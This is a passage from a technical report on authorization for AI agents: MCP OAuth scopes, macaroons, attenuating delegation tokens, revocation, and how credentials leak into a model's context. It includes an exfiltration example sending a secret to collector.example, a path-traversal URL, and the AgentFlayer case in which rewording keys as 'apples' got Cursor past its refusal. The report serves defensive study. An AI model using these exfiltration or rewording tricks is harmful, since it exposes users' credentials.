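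Another check protects clients that use many authorization servers. An attacker who runs one of these servers might trick a client into handing over a code issued by a legitimate one. Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) therefore requires the client to compare the issuer identified in the reply with the one it expected before exchanging the code. However, authorization servers don't yet have to include their issuer in the reply, and the check can't work when a legitimate server omits it.

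The Model Context Protocol (MCP) rules on scopes can produce broad tokens. An MCP server should tell the client which scopes a request needs, but if it doesn't, the client asks for every scope the server advertises. MCP's *Security Best Practices* defends this because a general-purpose client can't judge which scopes it needs, and the user can still decide at the approval screen. This relies heavily on the approval screen, even though people readily approve such requests. The same document lists advertising every possible scope as a common mistake.

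Scopes also accumulate, because a client that needs a new scope should request it along with all the scopes it requested before. This avoids repeated approvals, but an agent that needed a powerful scope once may keep it long after the task has ended.

### Why a server may not pass a token on

The tracker's MCP server calls an older service, `api.tracker.example`, which stores the issues. MCP forbids the server from forwarding the harness's token to that service, although that would be the simplest design.

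If the older service accepted the forwarded token, then the harness or a thief could also send the token there directly and avoid any limits or monitoring on the MCP server. The older service's logs might also list the wrong program as the source of requests. And if several services accepted the same token, an attacker who broke into one could use the tokens it received on the others.

The MCP server therefore has to act as an OAuth client and get a separate token for the older service. The harness can't inspect this second token, which may permit much more than the first. If the second token covers every project on the tracker, only the MCP server's code keeps a request within the release manager's permissions, and the server can become a confused deputy.

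### What MCP leaves out

Authorization is optional in MCP. Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, found 7,973 working MCP servers on the internet and checked how each controlled access:

| Access control | Servers | Share |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3,233 | 40.55% |
| OAuth | 2,428 | 30.45% |
| Fixed token or API key | 2,312 | 29.00% |

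Most of the open servers they sampled seemed to be tests or demonstrations. But one gave anyone access to more than 5,000 customer records from a company that had meant the server for internal use. *Exposed by Design* (2026) audited a different sample and found that 380 of 414 servers lacked OAuth. It also found 687 tools that let callers run shell commands without a credential.

Zhou and colleagues tested 119 servers that used OAuth and let new clients register automatically, and found at least one flaw in every one. The result may not hold for servers that don't allow automatic registration. Flaws in the registration process affected 96.6% of the sample. In one type, an attacker registers a client with the attacker's own return address, then sends a user a link to the genuine login page. If the user approves, the authorization code goes to the attacker. PKCE doesn't prevent this, because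 the attacker created the verifier. The July revision discourages automatic registration but still permits it for older systems.

OAuth also doesn't apply to MCP servers that the client starts on the user's machine and communicates with over standard input and output. Under the specification, these servers should get credentials from their environment instead. If `post_issue` ran this way with a permanent tracker key, the audience and expiry rules would not apply, and `run_tests` could inherit the key as before.

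### One request from `post_issue`

Suppose the release manager has approved the scope `issues:write`, and the model calls `post_issue` to report a failed test. The harness sends this request, shown here without some required fields:

```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Host: mcp.tracker.example
Authorization: Bearer eyJhbGciOi...
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: post_issue
Content-Type: application/json

{
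  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "post_issue",
    "arguments": {
      "project": "release",
      "title": "Installer test fails",
      "body": "The test stopped at step 4."
    }
  }
}
```

The server checks the token's signature, issuer, expiry, audience and scope. It then uses its own token to create the issue through `api.tracker.example`.

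The move to MCP has weakened the tool's URL scope. The old address contained `/projects/release/`, so the path limited the tool to one project. Now every tool on the server uses `/mcp`, and the model writes the project as an argument. The July revision requires the `Mcp-Name` header, so a proxy that decrypts traffic can identify the tool without reading the body, but the harness still has to check the argument to limit the project.

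The next table shows how the server would treat other uses of the token. In the third column, the token has the `authorization_details` entry for the `release` project, and in the fourth it also uses DPoP.

| Attempt | Scope, audience and expiry | With `authorization_details` | With DPoP too |
|---|---|---|---|
| Change the tracker's user accounts | Refuses | Refuses | Refuses |
| Create an issue in another project the release manager can reach | Accepts | Refuses | Refuses |
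| Use a copied token from the contributor's computer to post in `release` | Accepts | Accepts | Refuses |
| Put a password from the test output in an issue in `release` | Accepts | Accepts | Accepts |

The last two columns need more than basic MCP support, because Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* lists neither RFC 9396 nor DPoP among its standards. A simpler way to limit the token to one project is to give the agent its own tracker account, with access only to `release`, and have that account approve the token.

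None of these measures restricts the text of the issue. *Beyond OAuth* (2026) argues that finer scopes can't solve this, because a scope permits a type of action, while a user's request also specifies the details. If a user with a $500 limit tells an agent to pay $100, the limit still lets the agent pay $499. RFC 9396 lets a token specify an exact amount and payee, but only if whoever approves the token already knows them. The release agent writes its issue after the tests have run, so the release manager would have to approve each issue separately.

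### Addresses that the server fetches

The token's audience determines where the harness can use it, but doesn't restrict where the tracker's server sends its own requests. Suppose `post_issue` also accepts the address of an image, which the server downloads and attaches to the issue. A planted note could make the model supply `https://collector.example/image?key=` followed by a secret. The token is valid, so the server accepts the call and sends the secret to the contributor when it requests the image.

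The company's egress proxy can't block that download, because the request comes from the tracker's network. An attacker could also supply an address internal to that network. The tracker's owner therefore needs to check every address the server fetches. The harness should also check this argument against the same list of hosts used for links and images in an issue's text.

The harness faces a similar risk when it sets up OAuth. The MCP server sends it the location of a description of the authorization server, and that description contains more addresses for the harness to contact. A malicious MCP server could supply internal addresses. Model Context Protocol's security advice is to check these addresses much as a tool's requests are checked. The release agent can use a stricter rule, because its harness needs to contact only `mcp.tracker.example` and `auth.tracker.example` for this step.

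## Signed tokens that can be narrowed but not widened

Suppose the release agent uses three sub-agents, a reader, a tester and a reporter, and its harness holds a token that permits everything the release manager can do on the tracker. The reporter only needs to post issues in one project. Under ordinary OAuth, the harness can either give the reporter the full token or ask the authorization server for a narrower one. Some other tokens let the harness make the narrower one itself, without contacting anyone, which is called attenuation. The hard part is letting one holder add a restriction that the next holder can't remove.

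### A chain of keyed hashes

*Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014) solved this with a keyed hash, which is a short value that anyone with the secret key can compute from a message. Someone without the key can't produce the right value for a new message or work out the key from values they have seen. The usual method is HMAC, written HMAC(key, message).

A service such as the tracker creates a macaroon from a secret root key *K* and an identifier, `id`, that tells the service which root key it used. The macaroon's first signature is:

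```text
s₀ = HMAC(K, id)
```

A restriction on a macaroon is called a caveat, and it is a condition that every request must meet. Whoever adds caveat number *i* replaces the signature with a new one:

```text
sᵢ = HMAC(sᵢ₋₁, caveatᵢ)
```

The old signature is the key for the new one. The macaroon contains the identifier, the caveats in order, and only the latest signature.

A holder needs only the latest signature to add a caveat. To remove the last caveat, the holder would need the previous signature, which was the HMAC key used to compute the latest one. Nobody knows a practical way to recover that key from HMAC's output. Changing a caveat or swapping two of them fails for the same reason.

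Adding a looser caveat doesn't help an attacker either. The service requires every caveat to be true, so a macaroon that expires at 11:00 today still expires then, even if the attacker adds "time before 2030".

### Three caveats for the release agent

Suppose the tracker accepts macaroons at `api.tracker.example`. Each request names one of the tracker's tools, such as `post_issue` or `delete_issue`, which tells the server what to do. The harness starts with a macaroon that has no caveats, so it holds s₀. It adds a tool, an address prefix and an expiry time:

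```text
s₁ = HMAC(s₀, "tool = post_issue")
s₂ = HMAC(s₁, "address starts with https://api.tracker.example/projects/release/")
s₃ = HMAC(s₂, "time before 2026-12-05 11:00 UTC")
```

The harness gives the reporter the identifier, the three caveats and s₃. For each request, the tracker's server does the following:

1. Use the identifier to find *K*.
2. Compute the whole chain from *K*, the identifier and the caveats in the request. Refuse the request if the result differs from the signature the sender supplied.
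3. Put the address into its standard form and check each caveat against the request. Refuse the request if any caveat is false or unfamiliar.

Here are three requests that the server might receive at 10:40, all of them calls to `post_issue`:

| Path | Caveats in the macaroon | Signature | Caveats true? | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `/projects/release/issues` | All three | Matches | Yes | Accepts |
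| `/projects/payroll/issues` | All three | Matches | No, wrong address | Refuses |
| `/projects/payroll/issues` | Tool and expiry only | Doesn't match | Not checked | Refuses |

In the last request, someone has deleted the address caveat but kept s₃. The server computes HMAC(s₁, "time before 2026-12-05 11:00 UTC"), which doesn't match s₃. The sender would need s₁ to produce the right signature, and the reporter never had it.

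The reporter can still narrow its macaroon further. It could add "time before 2026-12-05 10:45 UTC" and pass the result to another program.

A macaroon starts with broad access, and each caveat removes some of it, so anything the caveats don't mention stays permitted. If the tracker's owner later lets `post_issue` attach an image from any web address, the reporter's macaroon will permit that too. Birgisson and colleagues describe a similar case where a storage service adds a delete operation after issuing macaroons that don't restrict operations. They suggest that the service refuse the new operation to old macaroons, or include a caveat about its own version from the start.

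### Proof from another service

Some conditions are hard for the tracker to check, such as whether the company is still working on this release. A third-party caveat requires proof from another service, in this case one that the company runs to keep track of releases. It works like this:

1. The harness picks a random key and encrypts two copies of it. One copy, together with the condition, is for the release service. The harness encrypts the other copy with the macaroon's current signature, so the tracker can read it.
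2. The harness adds both encrypted copies to the macaroon as a caveat.
3. The reporter sends the first copy to the release service, which decrypts it and checks the condition. If the condition is true, the service uses the key to create a second macaroon, perhaps valid for one minute.
4. The reporter sends both macaroons to the tracker. The tracker recomputes the chain, decrypts its copy of the key and uses it to check the second macaroon.

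The tracker never has to contact the release service or read the condition. If the company cancels the release, the release service stops issuing proofs, and the reporter loses access within a minute.

In step 4, the reporter also has to bind the second macaroon to the first, for example by hashing their signatures together. Otherwise, a dishonest server that received the proof could reuse it with a different macaroon.

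### From a shared secret to public keys

An ordinary macaroon is a bearer token. If a failing test prints the reporter's macaroon and the contributor gets a copy, the contributor can post issues in `release` until 11:00. A caveat that restricts requests to the release agent's IP address can reduce this risk. Birgisson and colleagues also describe a caveat that requires a signature from a particular private key, which would add proof of possession.

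A macaroon's other main limit is that checking it requires the secret root key, *K*. The company might want its egress proxy to refuse bad requests before they leave the network, but the proxy would need *K* to do so. Anyone with *K* can create a macaroon with no caveats, so the tracker's owner can't safely share *K*.

Public-key signatures avoid this problem because the key that checks a signature can't create one. In the version Birgisson and colleagues outline, each token comes with a fresh private key. To narrow the token, the holder creates a new pair of keys and uses the current private key to sign both the restriction and the new public key. The holder then passes on the longer token with the new private key, but keeps the old private key. Anyone with the issuer's public key can check each signature in turn.

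Biscuit, an open token format, uses public-key signatures in this way. It expresses restrictions in a form of Datalog, a small logic language made of facts and rules, so every verifier must run a Datalog engine. *Attenuating Authorization Tokens for Agentic Delegation Chains* (Niyikiza, 2026) states that people commonly use Biscuits as bearer tokens too.

Birgisson and colleagues preferred HMAC because it was faster. On their test server, an HMAC took 2.8 microseconds, an RSA signature took 458, and creating a pair of RSA keys took 54,000. RSA is an older public-key method, and newer ones such as Ed25519 create keys much faster. The difference is also negligible for an agent that waits seconds for a language model, so speed is now a weak reason to prefer HMAC's shared secret.

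### A token that lists tools and arguments

Niyikiza proposes Attenuating Authorization Tokens, a public-key format designed for agents. The proposal is an Internet-Draft, a working document submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), an internet standards body. The format builds on OAuth's `authorization_details` field and lists the agent's tools and the arguments each tool may receive.

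An authorization server issues the first token, called the root, to the harness. The harness can then sign child tokens for its sub-agents. Suppose the root lets the harness read issues and post them in two projects, `release` and `website`, until 11:00. The harness could give the reporter this child token, with the long values shortened:

```json
{
  "jti": "reporter-17",
  "iss": "urn:ietf:params:oauth:jwk-thumbprint:sha-256:...",
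  "iat": 1796466600,
  "exp": 1796467200,
  "del_depth": 1,
  "del_max_depth": 1,
  "par_hash": "...",
  "cnf": {"jwk": {"kty": "OKP", "crv": "Ed25519", "x": "..."}},
  "authorization_details": [{
    "type": "attenuating_agent_token",
    "tools": {
      "post_issue": {
        "project": {"constraint_type": "exact", "value": "release"},
        "title": {"constraint_type": "wildcard"},
        "body": {"constraint_type": "wildcard"}
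      }
    }
  }]
}
```

| Field | Meaning |
|---|---|
| `jti` | A unique name for the token |
| `iss` | A hash of the public key that checks this token's signature, here the harness's |
| `iat`, `exp` | When the token starts and expires, here 10:30 and 10:40 |
| `del_depth` | The number of steps from the root |
| `del_max_depth` | The greatest number of steps allowed; here the reporter can't create a child of its own |
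| `par_hash` | A hash of the parent token |
| `cnf` | The public key of the holder, here the reporter |
| `authorization_details` | The permitted tools and arguments |

The harness's ordinary code creates and signs this token. The model doesn't need to see the token or the private key.

### How the check keeps a child within its parent

The harness could sign a child token that permits more than the root does, and the signature would be valid. The enforcement point therefore compares every child with its parent. If C(*T*) is the set of all tool calls that token *T* permits, the rule is:

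```text
C(child) ⊆ C(parent)
```

In other words, the parent must permit every call that the child permits, as in CapScope. The draft defines how to compare each kind of constraint:

| Parent's constraint | Child's constraint | Accepted? |
|---|---|---|
| `project` is `release` or `website` | `project` is `release` | Yes |
| `project` is `release` or `website` | `project` is `release` or `payroll` | No, `payroll` is new |
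| `project` is `release` or `website` | `project` is anything except `payroll` | No, this permits other projects |
| `limit` is at most 100 | `limit` is at most 50 | Yes |
| `title` can be anything | `title` is "Installer test fails" | Yes |

If the draft has no rule for a pair of constraint types, the enforcement point rejects the chain. The child token also can't add a tool, expire later than its parent or raise the maximum depth.

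Macaroons don't need this comparison, because the service checks every caveat in the chain against the request. With Niyikiza's tokens, a mistake in the comparison code could let a child token permit more than its parent. Niyikiza describes the comparison rules as the new part of the design. Automated searches of cases with up to eight constraints and eight values have found no counterexample, but the formal verification isn't finished.

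#### Arguments that the token doesn't mention

Once a token restricts any argument of a tool, the enforcement point rejects calls that include an unlisted argument or omit a listed one. The reporter's token lists `project`, `title` and `body`, so a call that includes an `image` address fails, even if the tracker added image support after the harness signed the token. This closes the gap left by the three macaroon caveats.

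A drawback of this rule is that the token can't make a constrained argument optional. If `post_issue` accepts an optional label, the token must either require a label in every call or forbid labels. But an empty list of constraints, as in `"post_issue": {}`, permits any arguments.

When the parent names any arguments, the child must name exactly the same ones. The reporter's child cannot name an additional argument, although this may look like an extra restriction, because every call that the child permitted would then include an argument that the parent forbids.

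An enforcement point must also refuse a constraint type it doesn't recognize, because ignoring the constraint would remove a restriction the issuer wanted. This rule applies only inside the list of tools and arguments. Enforcement points ignore unfamiliar fields elsewhere in the token, so a company that invents a top-level field called `max_issues` can't expect other people's software to enforce it.

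#### What the parent hash prevents

The `par_hash` field contains the SHA-256 hash of the parent's encoded contents, which ties the child to that parent. Suppose the harness uses the same key for two root tokens, one for version 5.0 of the product and one for version 5.1, and both permit posting in `release`. Without the hash, someone could present a child made for 5.0 with the root for 5.1, and the signature, depth and permission checks could all pass.

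The reporter wouldn't gain access to another project this way, but its action would count as part of the wrong task. That matters if the company has approved work on only one version, or has revoked the token for the other.

#### Checking without a connection

The enforcement point needs only the tokens, the tool call, a fresh proof and the authorization server's public key. It carries out these checks:

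1. The authorization server signed the root.
2. The holder of each parent signed the child, the child contains the right parent hash, and its permissions lie within the parent's.
3. No token has expired.
4. The last token permits the tool and arguments.
5. The caller has signed this call with the private key that matches the last token.

The signature in the last step covers the tool's name, all its arguments and the time, so, unlike a DPoP proof, it also protects the text of an issue.

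Niyikiza recommends accepting a proof only within 30 seconds of its timestamp. Someone who copied a proof could still repeat the same call during that period. If a repeat would do harm, such as posting a duplicate issue, the enforcement point must keep a record of the proofs it has accepted. A company with several enforcement points may need to share this record between them, so offline checking may still require some communication.

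One token usually takes up 1 to 4 kilobytes, and a chain of two or more often exceeds the size limit that web servers set for headers, so Niyikiza advises putting the chain in the request body.

These checks don't show whether the harness chose a sensible restriction. Planted text could lead the harness to sign a valid child token for the wrong project, much as planted text misled CapScope's orchestrator. Niyikiza gives this as one reason to limit the depth of a chain, since every extra holder makes choices that the enforcement point has to trust.

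### Why addresses are outside the core

The draft's core constraints can permit a list of exact addresses, but they can't permit all addresses under a prefix such as `https://docs.example.com/guide/`. Niyikiza left out rules for URLs and file paths because different verifiers have to reach the same result, both when they check a call and when they compare a child token with its parent.

Verifiers must agree on the standard form of a URL to check a call. Suppose a token allows only URLs under `https://docs.example.com/guide/`, and the agent requests `https://docs.example.com/guide/%2e%2e/admin/export`. A verifier that decodes the dots and resolves the path to `/admin/export` refuses the call, while one that only compares the start of the text accepts it.

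To compare two tokens, verifiers must agree on whether one pattern contains another. Suppose the parent permits `example.com` and the child permits `docs.example.com`. The child would be a valid narrowing under the rules of GitHub's firewall, which include subdomains, but invalid under Codex's rules, because it permits a host that the parent doesn't.

This is less of a problem for an ordinary macaroon, because the service that creates it also checks it. The tracker can choose its own rules for addresses, and no other verifier has to use the same ones.

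A similar danger affects other arguments. *Transaction-Bound Authorization Tokens for Software and AI Agents (SPT-Txn)* (Coetzee, 2026) describes a system that binds a token to a hash of one specific tool call. Suppose the call contains two fields named `project`, with the values `release` and `payroll`. If the issuer's program reads the first and the verifier's program reads the last, a token for `release` could authorize a post in `payroll`. Coetzee ranks this kind of mismatch as the most likely serious risk. The draft requires the issuer and verifier to use the same code to produce the call's standard form, and to reject duplicate fields.

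*Verifiable Attenuated Delegation for AI Agent Chains* (Asor, 2026) takes a simpler approach and includes a `prefix` constraint that compares text. Two prefixes are easy to compare because the child's must start with the parent's. But the constraint's definition doesn't require an enforcement point to resolve any `..` in a path first, so an address can match the prefix and still lead outside the permitted directory.

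Niyikiza's draft lets people add constraint types through a public registry. Anyone who adds one must define a comparison that always finishes, never accepts a child constraint broader than its parent, and gives the same result in every program. The draft sketches an example type for file paths. Even after someone registers a type for web addresses, an enforcement point that doesn't support it must refuse the token. For now, the company could list every page of its guide in the reader's token, or leave the prefix check for `read_docs` in the harness.

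### Madden's objection about parent tokens

Niyikiza announced the draft on the OAuth working group's mailing list on 15 June 2026. Neil Madden (2026) replied the same day and asked why the draft didn't use macaroons. When a holder adds a caveat to a macaroon, the new signature replaces the old one, so the next holder can't go back to the broader version. Niyikiza's chain has to include every parent token because the enforcement point checks them all, so the reporter receives a full copy of the root token. Madden asked what would stop a sub-agent from presenting the root token itself.

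Niyikiza (2026) replies that every token is bound to its holder's key, so the reporter can copy the root token but can't use it without the harness's private key. The parent token deliberately stays valid, because a harness may need to create several child tokens and still make its own calls. Niyikiza chose public keys over HMAC so that organizations could check each other's tokens without sharing a secret.

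Niyikiza accepted that a stolen key exposes the full authority of its token until the token expires or someone revokes it. He also assumed that agents don't share private keys. If code in a test read the harness's key, an attacker could use it with a copy of the root token to do everything the harness can do on the tracker.

But a macaroon doesn't remove this danger, because the harness still has s₀ and needs to protect it. Niyikiza's tokens are safer than macaroons when they leak through text, because the private key doesn't leak with them. Anyone who finds a macaroon in an issue can use it within its caveats.

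### Revocation and offline checking

OAuth has a standard way to obtain a narrower token, called Token Exchange (RFC 8693). The harness sends its token to the authorization server and requests one with less access. The server determines what to grant and issues the new token. This avoids a chain of signatures, but the harness has to contact the server every time it delegates work.

The new token can include an `act` field that records which agents took part. Asor points out that a service is supposed to consider only the current agent when deciding whether to allow a request, so the earlier names don't restrict anything. *Delegation Chain for OAuth 2.0* (Liu, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) proposes another field to record the restrictions that applied at each step.

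*Credential Delegation Protocol for AI Agents in Multi-System Environments* (Sweeney, 2026) cites a weakness reported to the OAuth working group in February 2026. A compromised agent can send the server a user's token from one task and an agent's token from another. The server may then sign a token that records a delegation that never happened.

A server can refuse to help once a token has been revoked, but an offline verifier gets no notice of the revocation. Niyikiza's draft has no way to revoke a single token and relies on short lifetimes. Asor and Coetzee add status lists, signed lists of revoked tokens that a verifier regularly downloads and stores. Sweeney requires a server at every step, including each use of a token. That server must block a revoked token within one second and all its descendants within five.

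Suppose someone steals the reporter's private key, and the company finds out at 10:32. The reporter's token expires at 10:40.

| Method | Does each tool call need a server that tracks revocation? | When the thief loses access |
|---|---|---|
| Expiry only | No | 10:40 |
| Status list downloaded every five minutes | No, but the verifier needs regular downloads | By 10:37 |
| Server in every step | Yes | Within one second of revocation |

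The methods also differ in how they handle a network outage. With expiry only, the enforcement point can keep checking calls, although the harness will eventually need a new root token. Under Coetzee's rules, a verifier must refuse a token that refers to a status list if the verifier has no current copy of the list, so a long outage stops the work. If Sweeney's server is down, no agent that depends on it can act.

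A service that checks its own macaroons can revoke them more easily. If it stores a separate root key for each original macaroon, deleting that key immediately disables the macaroon and every narrower one made from it.

Subramanian and Sengupta (2026), in *Crypto-bound identity-verified capability tokens for coordinating distributed AI agents*, consider revocation "extremely hard or even impossible" when verification is purely offline. They discuss three ways around this:

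- Agents could use tokens that last about five minutes and renew them. A revoked token would fail at its next renewal.
- The service could check the status of every parent in the chain. This makes it possible to cancel any branch, but longer chains take longer to check.
- The issuer could publish a cryptographic accumulator, a short value that represents all the valid tokens. Each token would carry evidence that it belongs to the set. Verifiers would still need the latest value, and the cryptography is complicated.

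Subramanian and Sengupta conclude that the delay from an online check is usually worth accepting, since most agents have a network connection. This is true of the release agent, because the tracker's server has to be online to accept an issue and can look up the token in its own records at the same time. Offline checking is more useful when the verifier belongs to another organization, when connections are unreliable, or when a harness creates so many sub-agents that the authorization server would become a bottleneck.

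Asor describes the two approaches as two parts of one design, in which an online server issues and revokes tokens while enforcement points still check the full chain.

### Status and use of the drafts

RFC 8693 is a published standard. The proposals from Niyikiza, Asor, Coetzee, Sweeney, and Liu and colleagues are individual drafts, meaning they come from their authors and not from an IETF working group. *An Attenuated Delegation Profile for Automated Agents* (Hassan, 2026) is also an individual draft, and it puts a chain of narrowing steps in a web request's header.

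Sweeney counts several dozen individual drafts on agent identity or delegation, so these designs have a lot of competition. The OAuth working group changed its charter in June 2026 to cover agents that act for users, but that doesn't commit it to any of the designs. Asor hopes to merge with the proposals from Niyikiza and Coetzee, and already uses several of Niyikiza's field names, including `par_hash`.

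In October 2026, the latest version of Niyikiza's draft was still 01, which expires on 17 December. It doesn't include the comparison with macaroons that Niyikiza had promised Madden to add to the security section.

Niyikiza's draft lists only one implementation, a reference version from Tenuo, Niyikiza's own company. It can create child tokens and check chains. Coetzee also refers to a public reference implementation, and tightened the rules for issuing tokens after a security review of it. Neither draft reports use in a working product. The release agent could use one of these formats with the tracker only if the tracker's owner added support for it.

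## How credentials get into a model's text

A narrow token limits what a thief can do with it, but the thief must first get a copy. Credentials can reach the model in more than one way, such as when a failing test prints the release agent's tracker key. If the model then writes the key in several places, the contributor who planted the note needs to see only one of them.

### From the source to the reader

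Here are five ways a credential could enter the release agent's context:

| Way in | Example |
|---|---|
| Prompt | The release manager pastes the tracker key into the chat and asks why it doesn't work |
| File | The agent opens a settings file that contains a database password |
| Program output | A failing test prints its environment variables |
| Error message | A failed database connection reports the full address it tried, including the password |
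| Tool result | The agent reads an old issue in which an engineer once pasted a key |

The model can then write the credential into text that other people read:

| Way out | Who can read it |
|---|---|
| Reply | Everyone in the conversation |
| Tool argument | The service that the tool contacts, and anyone who can see what the service stores |
| Committed code (code saved in a project's version history) | Everyone with access to the project, even after someone deletes the line |
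| Log | Whoever runs the logging system |
| Saved transcript | Anyone who can open the history, and any later session that loads it |

When a user pastes a key into a chat, software may copy it into the conversation history, logs, a memory store, generated code and error reports without any attack, according to *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026). The researchers work for Corvic AI, which sells a way to keep keys out of chats, but their point doesn't depend on the product. Systems such as logs and memory stores exist to retain text, so deleting the original message leaves the other copies in place, and the user has to revoke the key at the service that issued it.

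GitGuardian sells software for finding leaked credentials. Its report *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* found that, of a set of credentials that worked in 2022, more than 64% still worked in January 2026.

An agent can also pick up credentials with no attacker involved. In *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords*, Udinmwen (2026) reports that a coding assistant couldn't find its configuration file during a routine code review, so it read all the variables on the computer and leaked live passwords.

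An agent that searches this widely will often find credentials. GitGuardian found 33,185 different credentials in data that the Shai-Hulud 2 malware had stolen from 6,943 computers, most of them servers that build and test software automatically. Each credential that still worked appeared in about eight places on the same machine, so hiding one file from an agent would leave roughly seven other copies. Credentials also turn up in the workplace tools that agents read. About 28% of the incidents GitGuardian studied began entirely outside code repositories, in places such as Slack and the issue tracker Jira.

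### Debug messages that reach the model

The release agent's failing test is an example of a common problem. Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, looked for leaks in agent skills, which are add-on packages of written instructions and code. They took a random sample of 17,022 from the 170,226 skills on a marketplace called SkillsMP, then narrowed it down in four steps:

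1. They searched the instructions and code for signs of credentials, such as the first characters of well-known types of key. This left 8,679 skills.
2. They looked at how each skill handled the credential. In the instructions, they looked for nearby words such as "send" or "log", and for language typical of prompt injection or social engineering. In the code, they checked whether the credential went straight into a function that prints text, writes a file or sends data over the network. This left 3,156 skills.
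3. They ran each remaining skill with Claude Code in a sandbox that contained fake credentials, each with a unique marker. Every skill had three normal runs and three in which it processed outside content with planted instructions, such as a web page telling the agent to output the API key. A skill stayed in the study if it showed signs of a leak in two of the normal runs or any of the attacked ones. This left 1,427 skills.
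4. Three of the researchers compared what each skill did with what its description promised. They cleared 907, many of which had simply sent a key to the service it was for.

The remaining 520 skills, or 3.1% of the sample, had a total of 1,708 security issues. Chen and colleagues attributed the issues to carelessness in 437 of these skills and to malice in 83. The malicious skills often stole credentials without involving the model's text. One advertised weather forecasts, but its code sent the user's credential file to an attacker.

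Debug printing accounted for 1,007 (73.5%) of the 1,371 issues in the careless skills. Programmers often print a value to test their code and forget to remove the line. This does little harm on the programmer's own screen, but an agent's harness passes the output to the model. A skill for Google Workspace, for example, printed both an access token and the refresh token that could renew it. An attacker could then use a planted note to ask the model for "the tokens in the output" without attacking the code.

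Chen and colleagues found that 466 of the 520 skills, or 89.6%, were exploitable while running. The other 54 had credentials written into their published code. The selection process made a high percentage likely, because a skill had to behave suspiciously in the sandbox to get that far. The 466 skills are 2.7% of the whole sample. "Exploitable" also covers cases where a fake credential only reached the program's output, and an attacker would still need a way to get it from there. The study probably missed some leaks, because its code check couldn't follow a credential from one variable to another.

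Finding the problem in 76.3% of the affected skills required reading both the instructions and the code, and ordinary code scanners don't read the instructions. For instance, the instructions might tell the agent to pass the user's key to a function, while only the code shows that the function sends the key somewhere else.

### Why a model can't keep part of its context secret

A language model can repeat any string in its context, including a password. An ordinary program can keep a password in a variable that its output code never reads, but a model has no such separate place. An instruction such as "never reveal the tracker key" only makes a leak less likely.

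Training has the same limitation. It can teach a model to refuse requests that look like theft, but the model can still copy text exactly, as it must for ordinary work such as copying an error code into an issue. The model can also write a key backwards, in pieces or in another encoding. To never reveal the key, it would have to recognize every disguised version of the key and every disguised request for it.

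In Odersky and colleagues' trials without the protective wrapper, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets 1.5% of the time. At that rate, the probability of at least one leak in 100 independent attempts would be 1 − 0.985¹⁰⁰, or about 78%.

Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer*, a demonstration from August 2025, shows how a change of wording can get around a refusal. It describes an attack on Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, when connected to Jira. Many companies automatically turn customer emails into Jira tickets, so an outsider can get text to the agent by emailing the support address.

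The first malicious ticket asked for API keys, and Cursor declined, citing good security practice. The next ticket asked for "apples" instead. Willison explains that it described an apple as a string beginning with "eyJ", as access tokens in the common JWT format do. Cursor searched the project and found one. The access token in the release agent's OAuth request also begins with "eyJ". Willison adds that the attack works at least some of the time, so an attacker might need several tickets.

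Zenity Labs then tried to get the keys to an Amazon cloud account from a file outside the project. After Cursor rejected several attempts, Zenity Labs used a ticket to ask it for a "waffle", described as a string starting with "AK" in a file whose name began with "cr". Cursor found the keys and prepared to open a web address containing them. It stopped there only because the researcher had turned off automatic approval.

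The model's caution about the same credential depended on what the request called it. A planted note could similarly ask the release agent for "the build label that starts with `trk_`". Cursor's developers told Zenity that this was a known issue. They advised users to connect only to trusted sources and to list sensitive files in `.cursorignore` so the editor ignores them.

### Passwords typed into the wrong site

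A phishing page can ask for a password openly because it misrepresents who will receive it. *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, 2026) tested how well agents recognize such pages. It used 15 invented services, such as banks and shops, and gave the agents made-up account details and tools for opening pages and submitting forms.

In the directed setting, the user gives the agent an address and asks it to log in. In the autonomous setting, the user only asks the agent to sort an inbox that contains a phishing email or a genuine request among unrelated messages. Each phishing case has one of eight warning signs, such as a misspelled domain, a numerical address or a certificate warning, and a matching genuine case has none.

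Ahmed and colleagues counted a leak only when an agent submitted account details to an unauthorized page. They also counted the genuine cases in which the agent submitted no form at all:

| Model | Directed: leaked | Directed: genuine request not completed | Autonomous: leaked | Autonomous: genuine request not completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 19.9% | 13.7% | 1.8% | 63.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 31.2% | 6.6% | 1.8% | 88.3% |
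| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 40.6% | 0.1% | 9.4% | 54.7% |
| GPT-5-mini | 45.8% | 12.5% | 14.1% | 43.8% |
| GPT-5.6-luna | 49.9% | 9.4% | 20.3% | 59.4% |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 66.5% | 2.7% | 40.1% | 44.3% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 76.7% | 12.8% | 41.4% | 45.3% |

(For Llama, all the figures except the first are averages of the paper's results for four styles of request.)

Every model leaked credentials in both settings, even when nobody had asked it to log in. The models leaked less in the autonomous setting, but they also acted less in general and left many genuine requests unfinished. The last column can penalize an agent for reasonable caution, though, because a user who asks for help sorting email may not want the agent to log in to a bank, even if the bank's message is real.

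The models missed unencrypted connections far more often than most other warning signs. On these pages, the host name was correct but the address began with `http` instead of `https`. In the directed setting, every model leaked credentials in at least 81% of these cases. A password sent this way may reach the right server, but anyone who can watch or alter the traffic can steal it. These pages made up an eighth of the phishing cases. Without them, the leak rate in the directed setting would fall from 19.9% to about 10% for Sonnet 5, and from 31.2% to about 23% for Opus 4.8.

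Giving the models the official domains and telling them to check the page's domain against these before entering anything helped most. In the directed setting, this made five of the seven models both safer and more likely to complete genuine requests. GPT-5-mini's leak rate fell from 71.9% to 22.4%, and the share of genuine requests it left unfinished from 25.0% to 1.6%. General advice to act safely helped much less, and Opus 4.8 leaked slightly more often with it. When the user's request urged caution, models leaked less, but most also completed fewer genuine logins.

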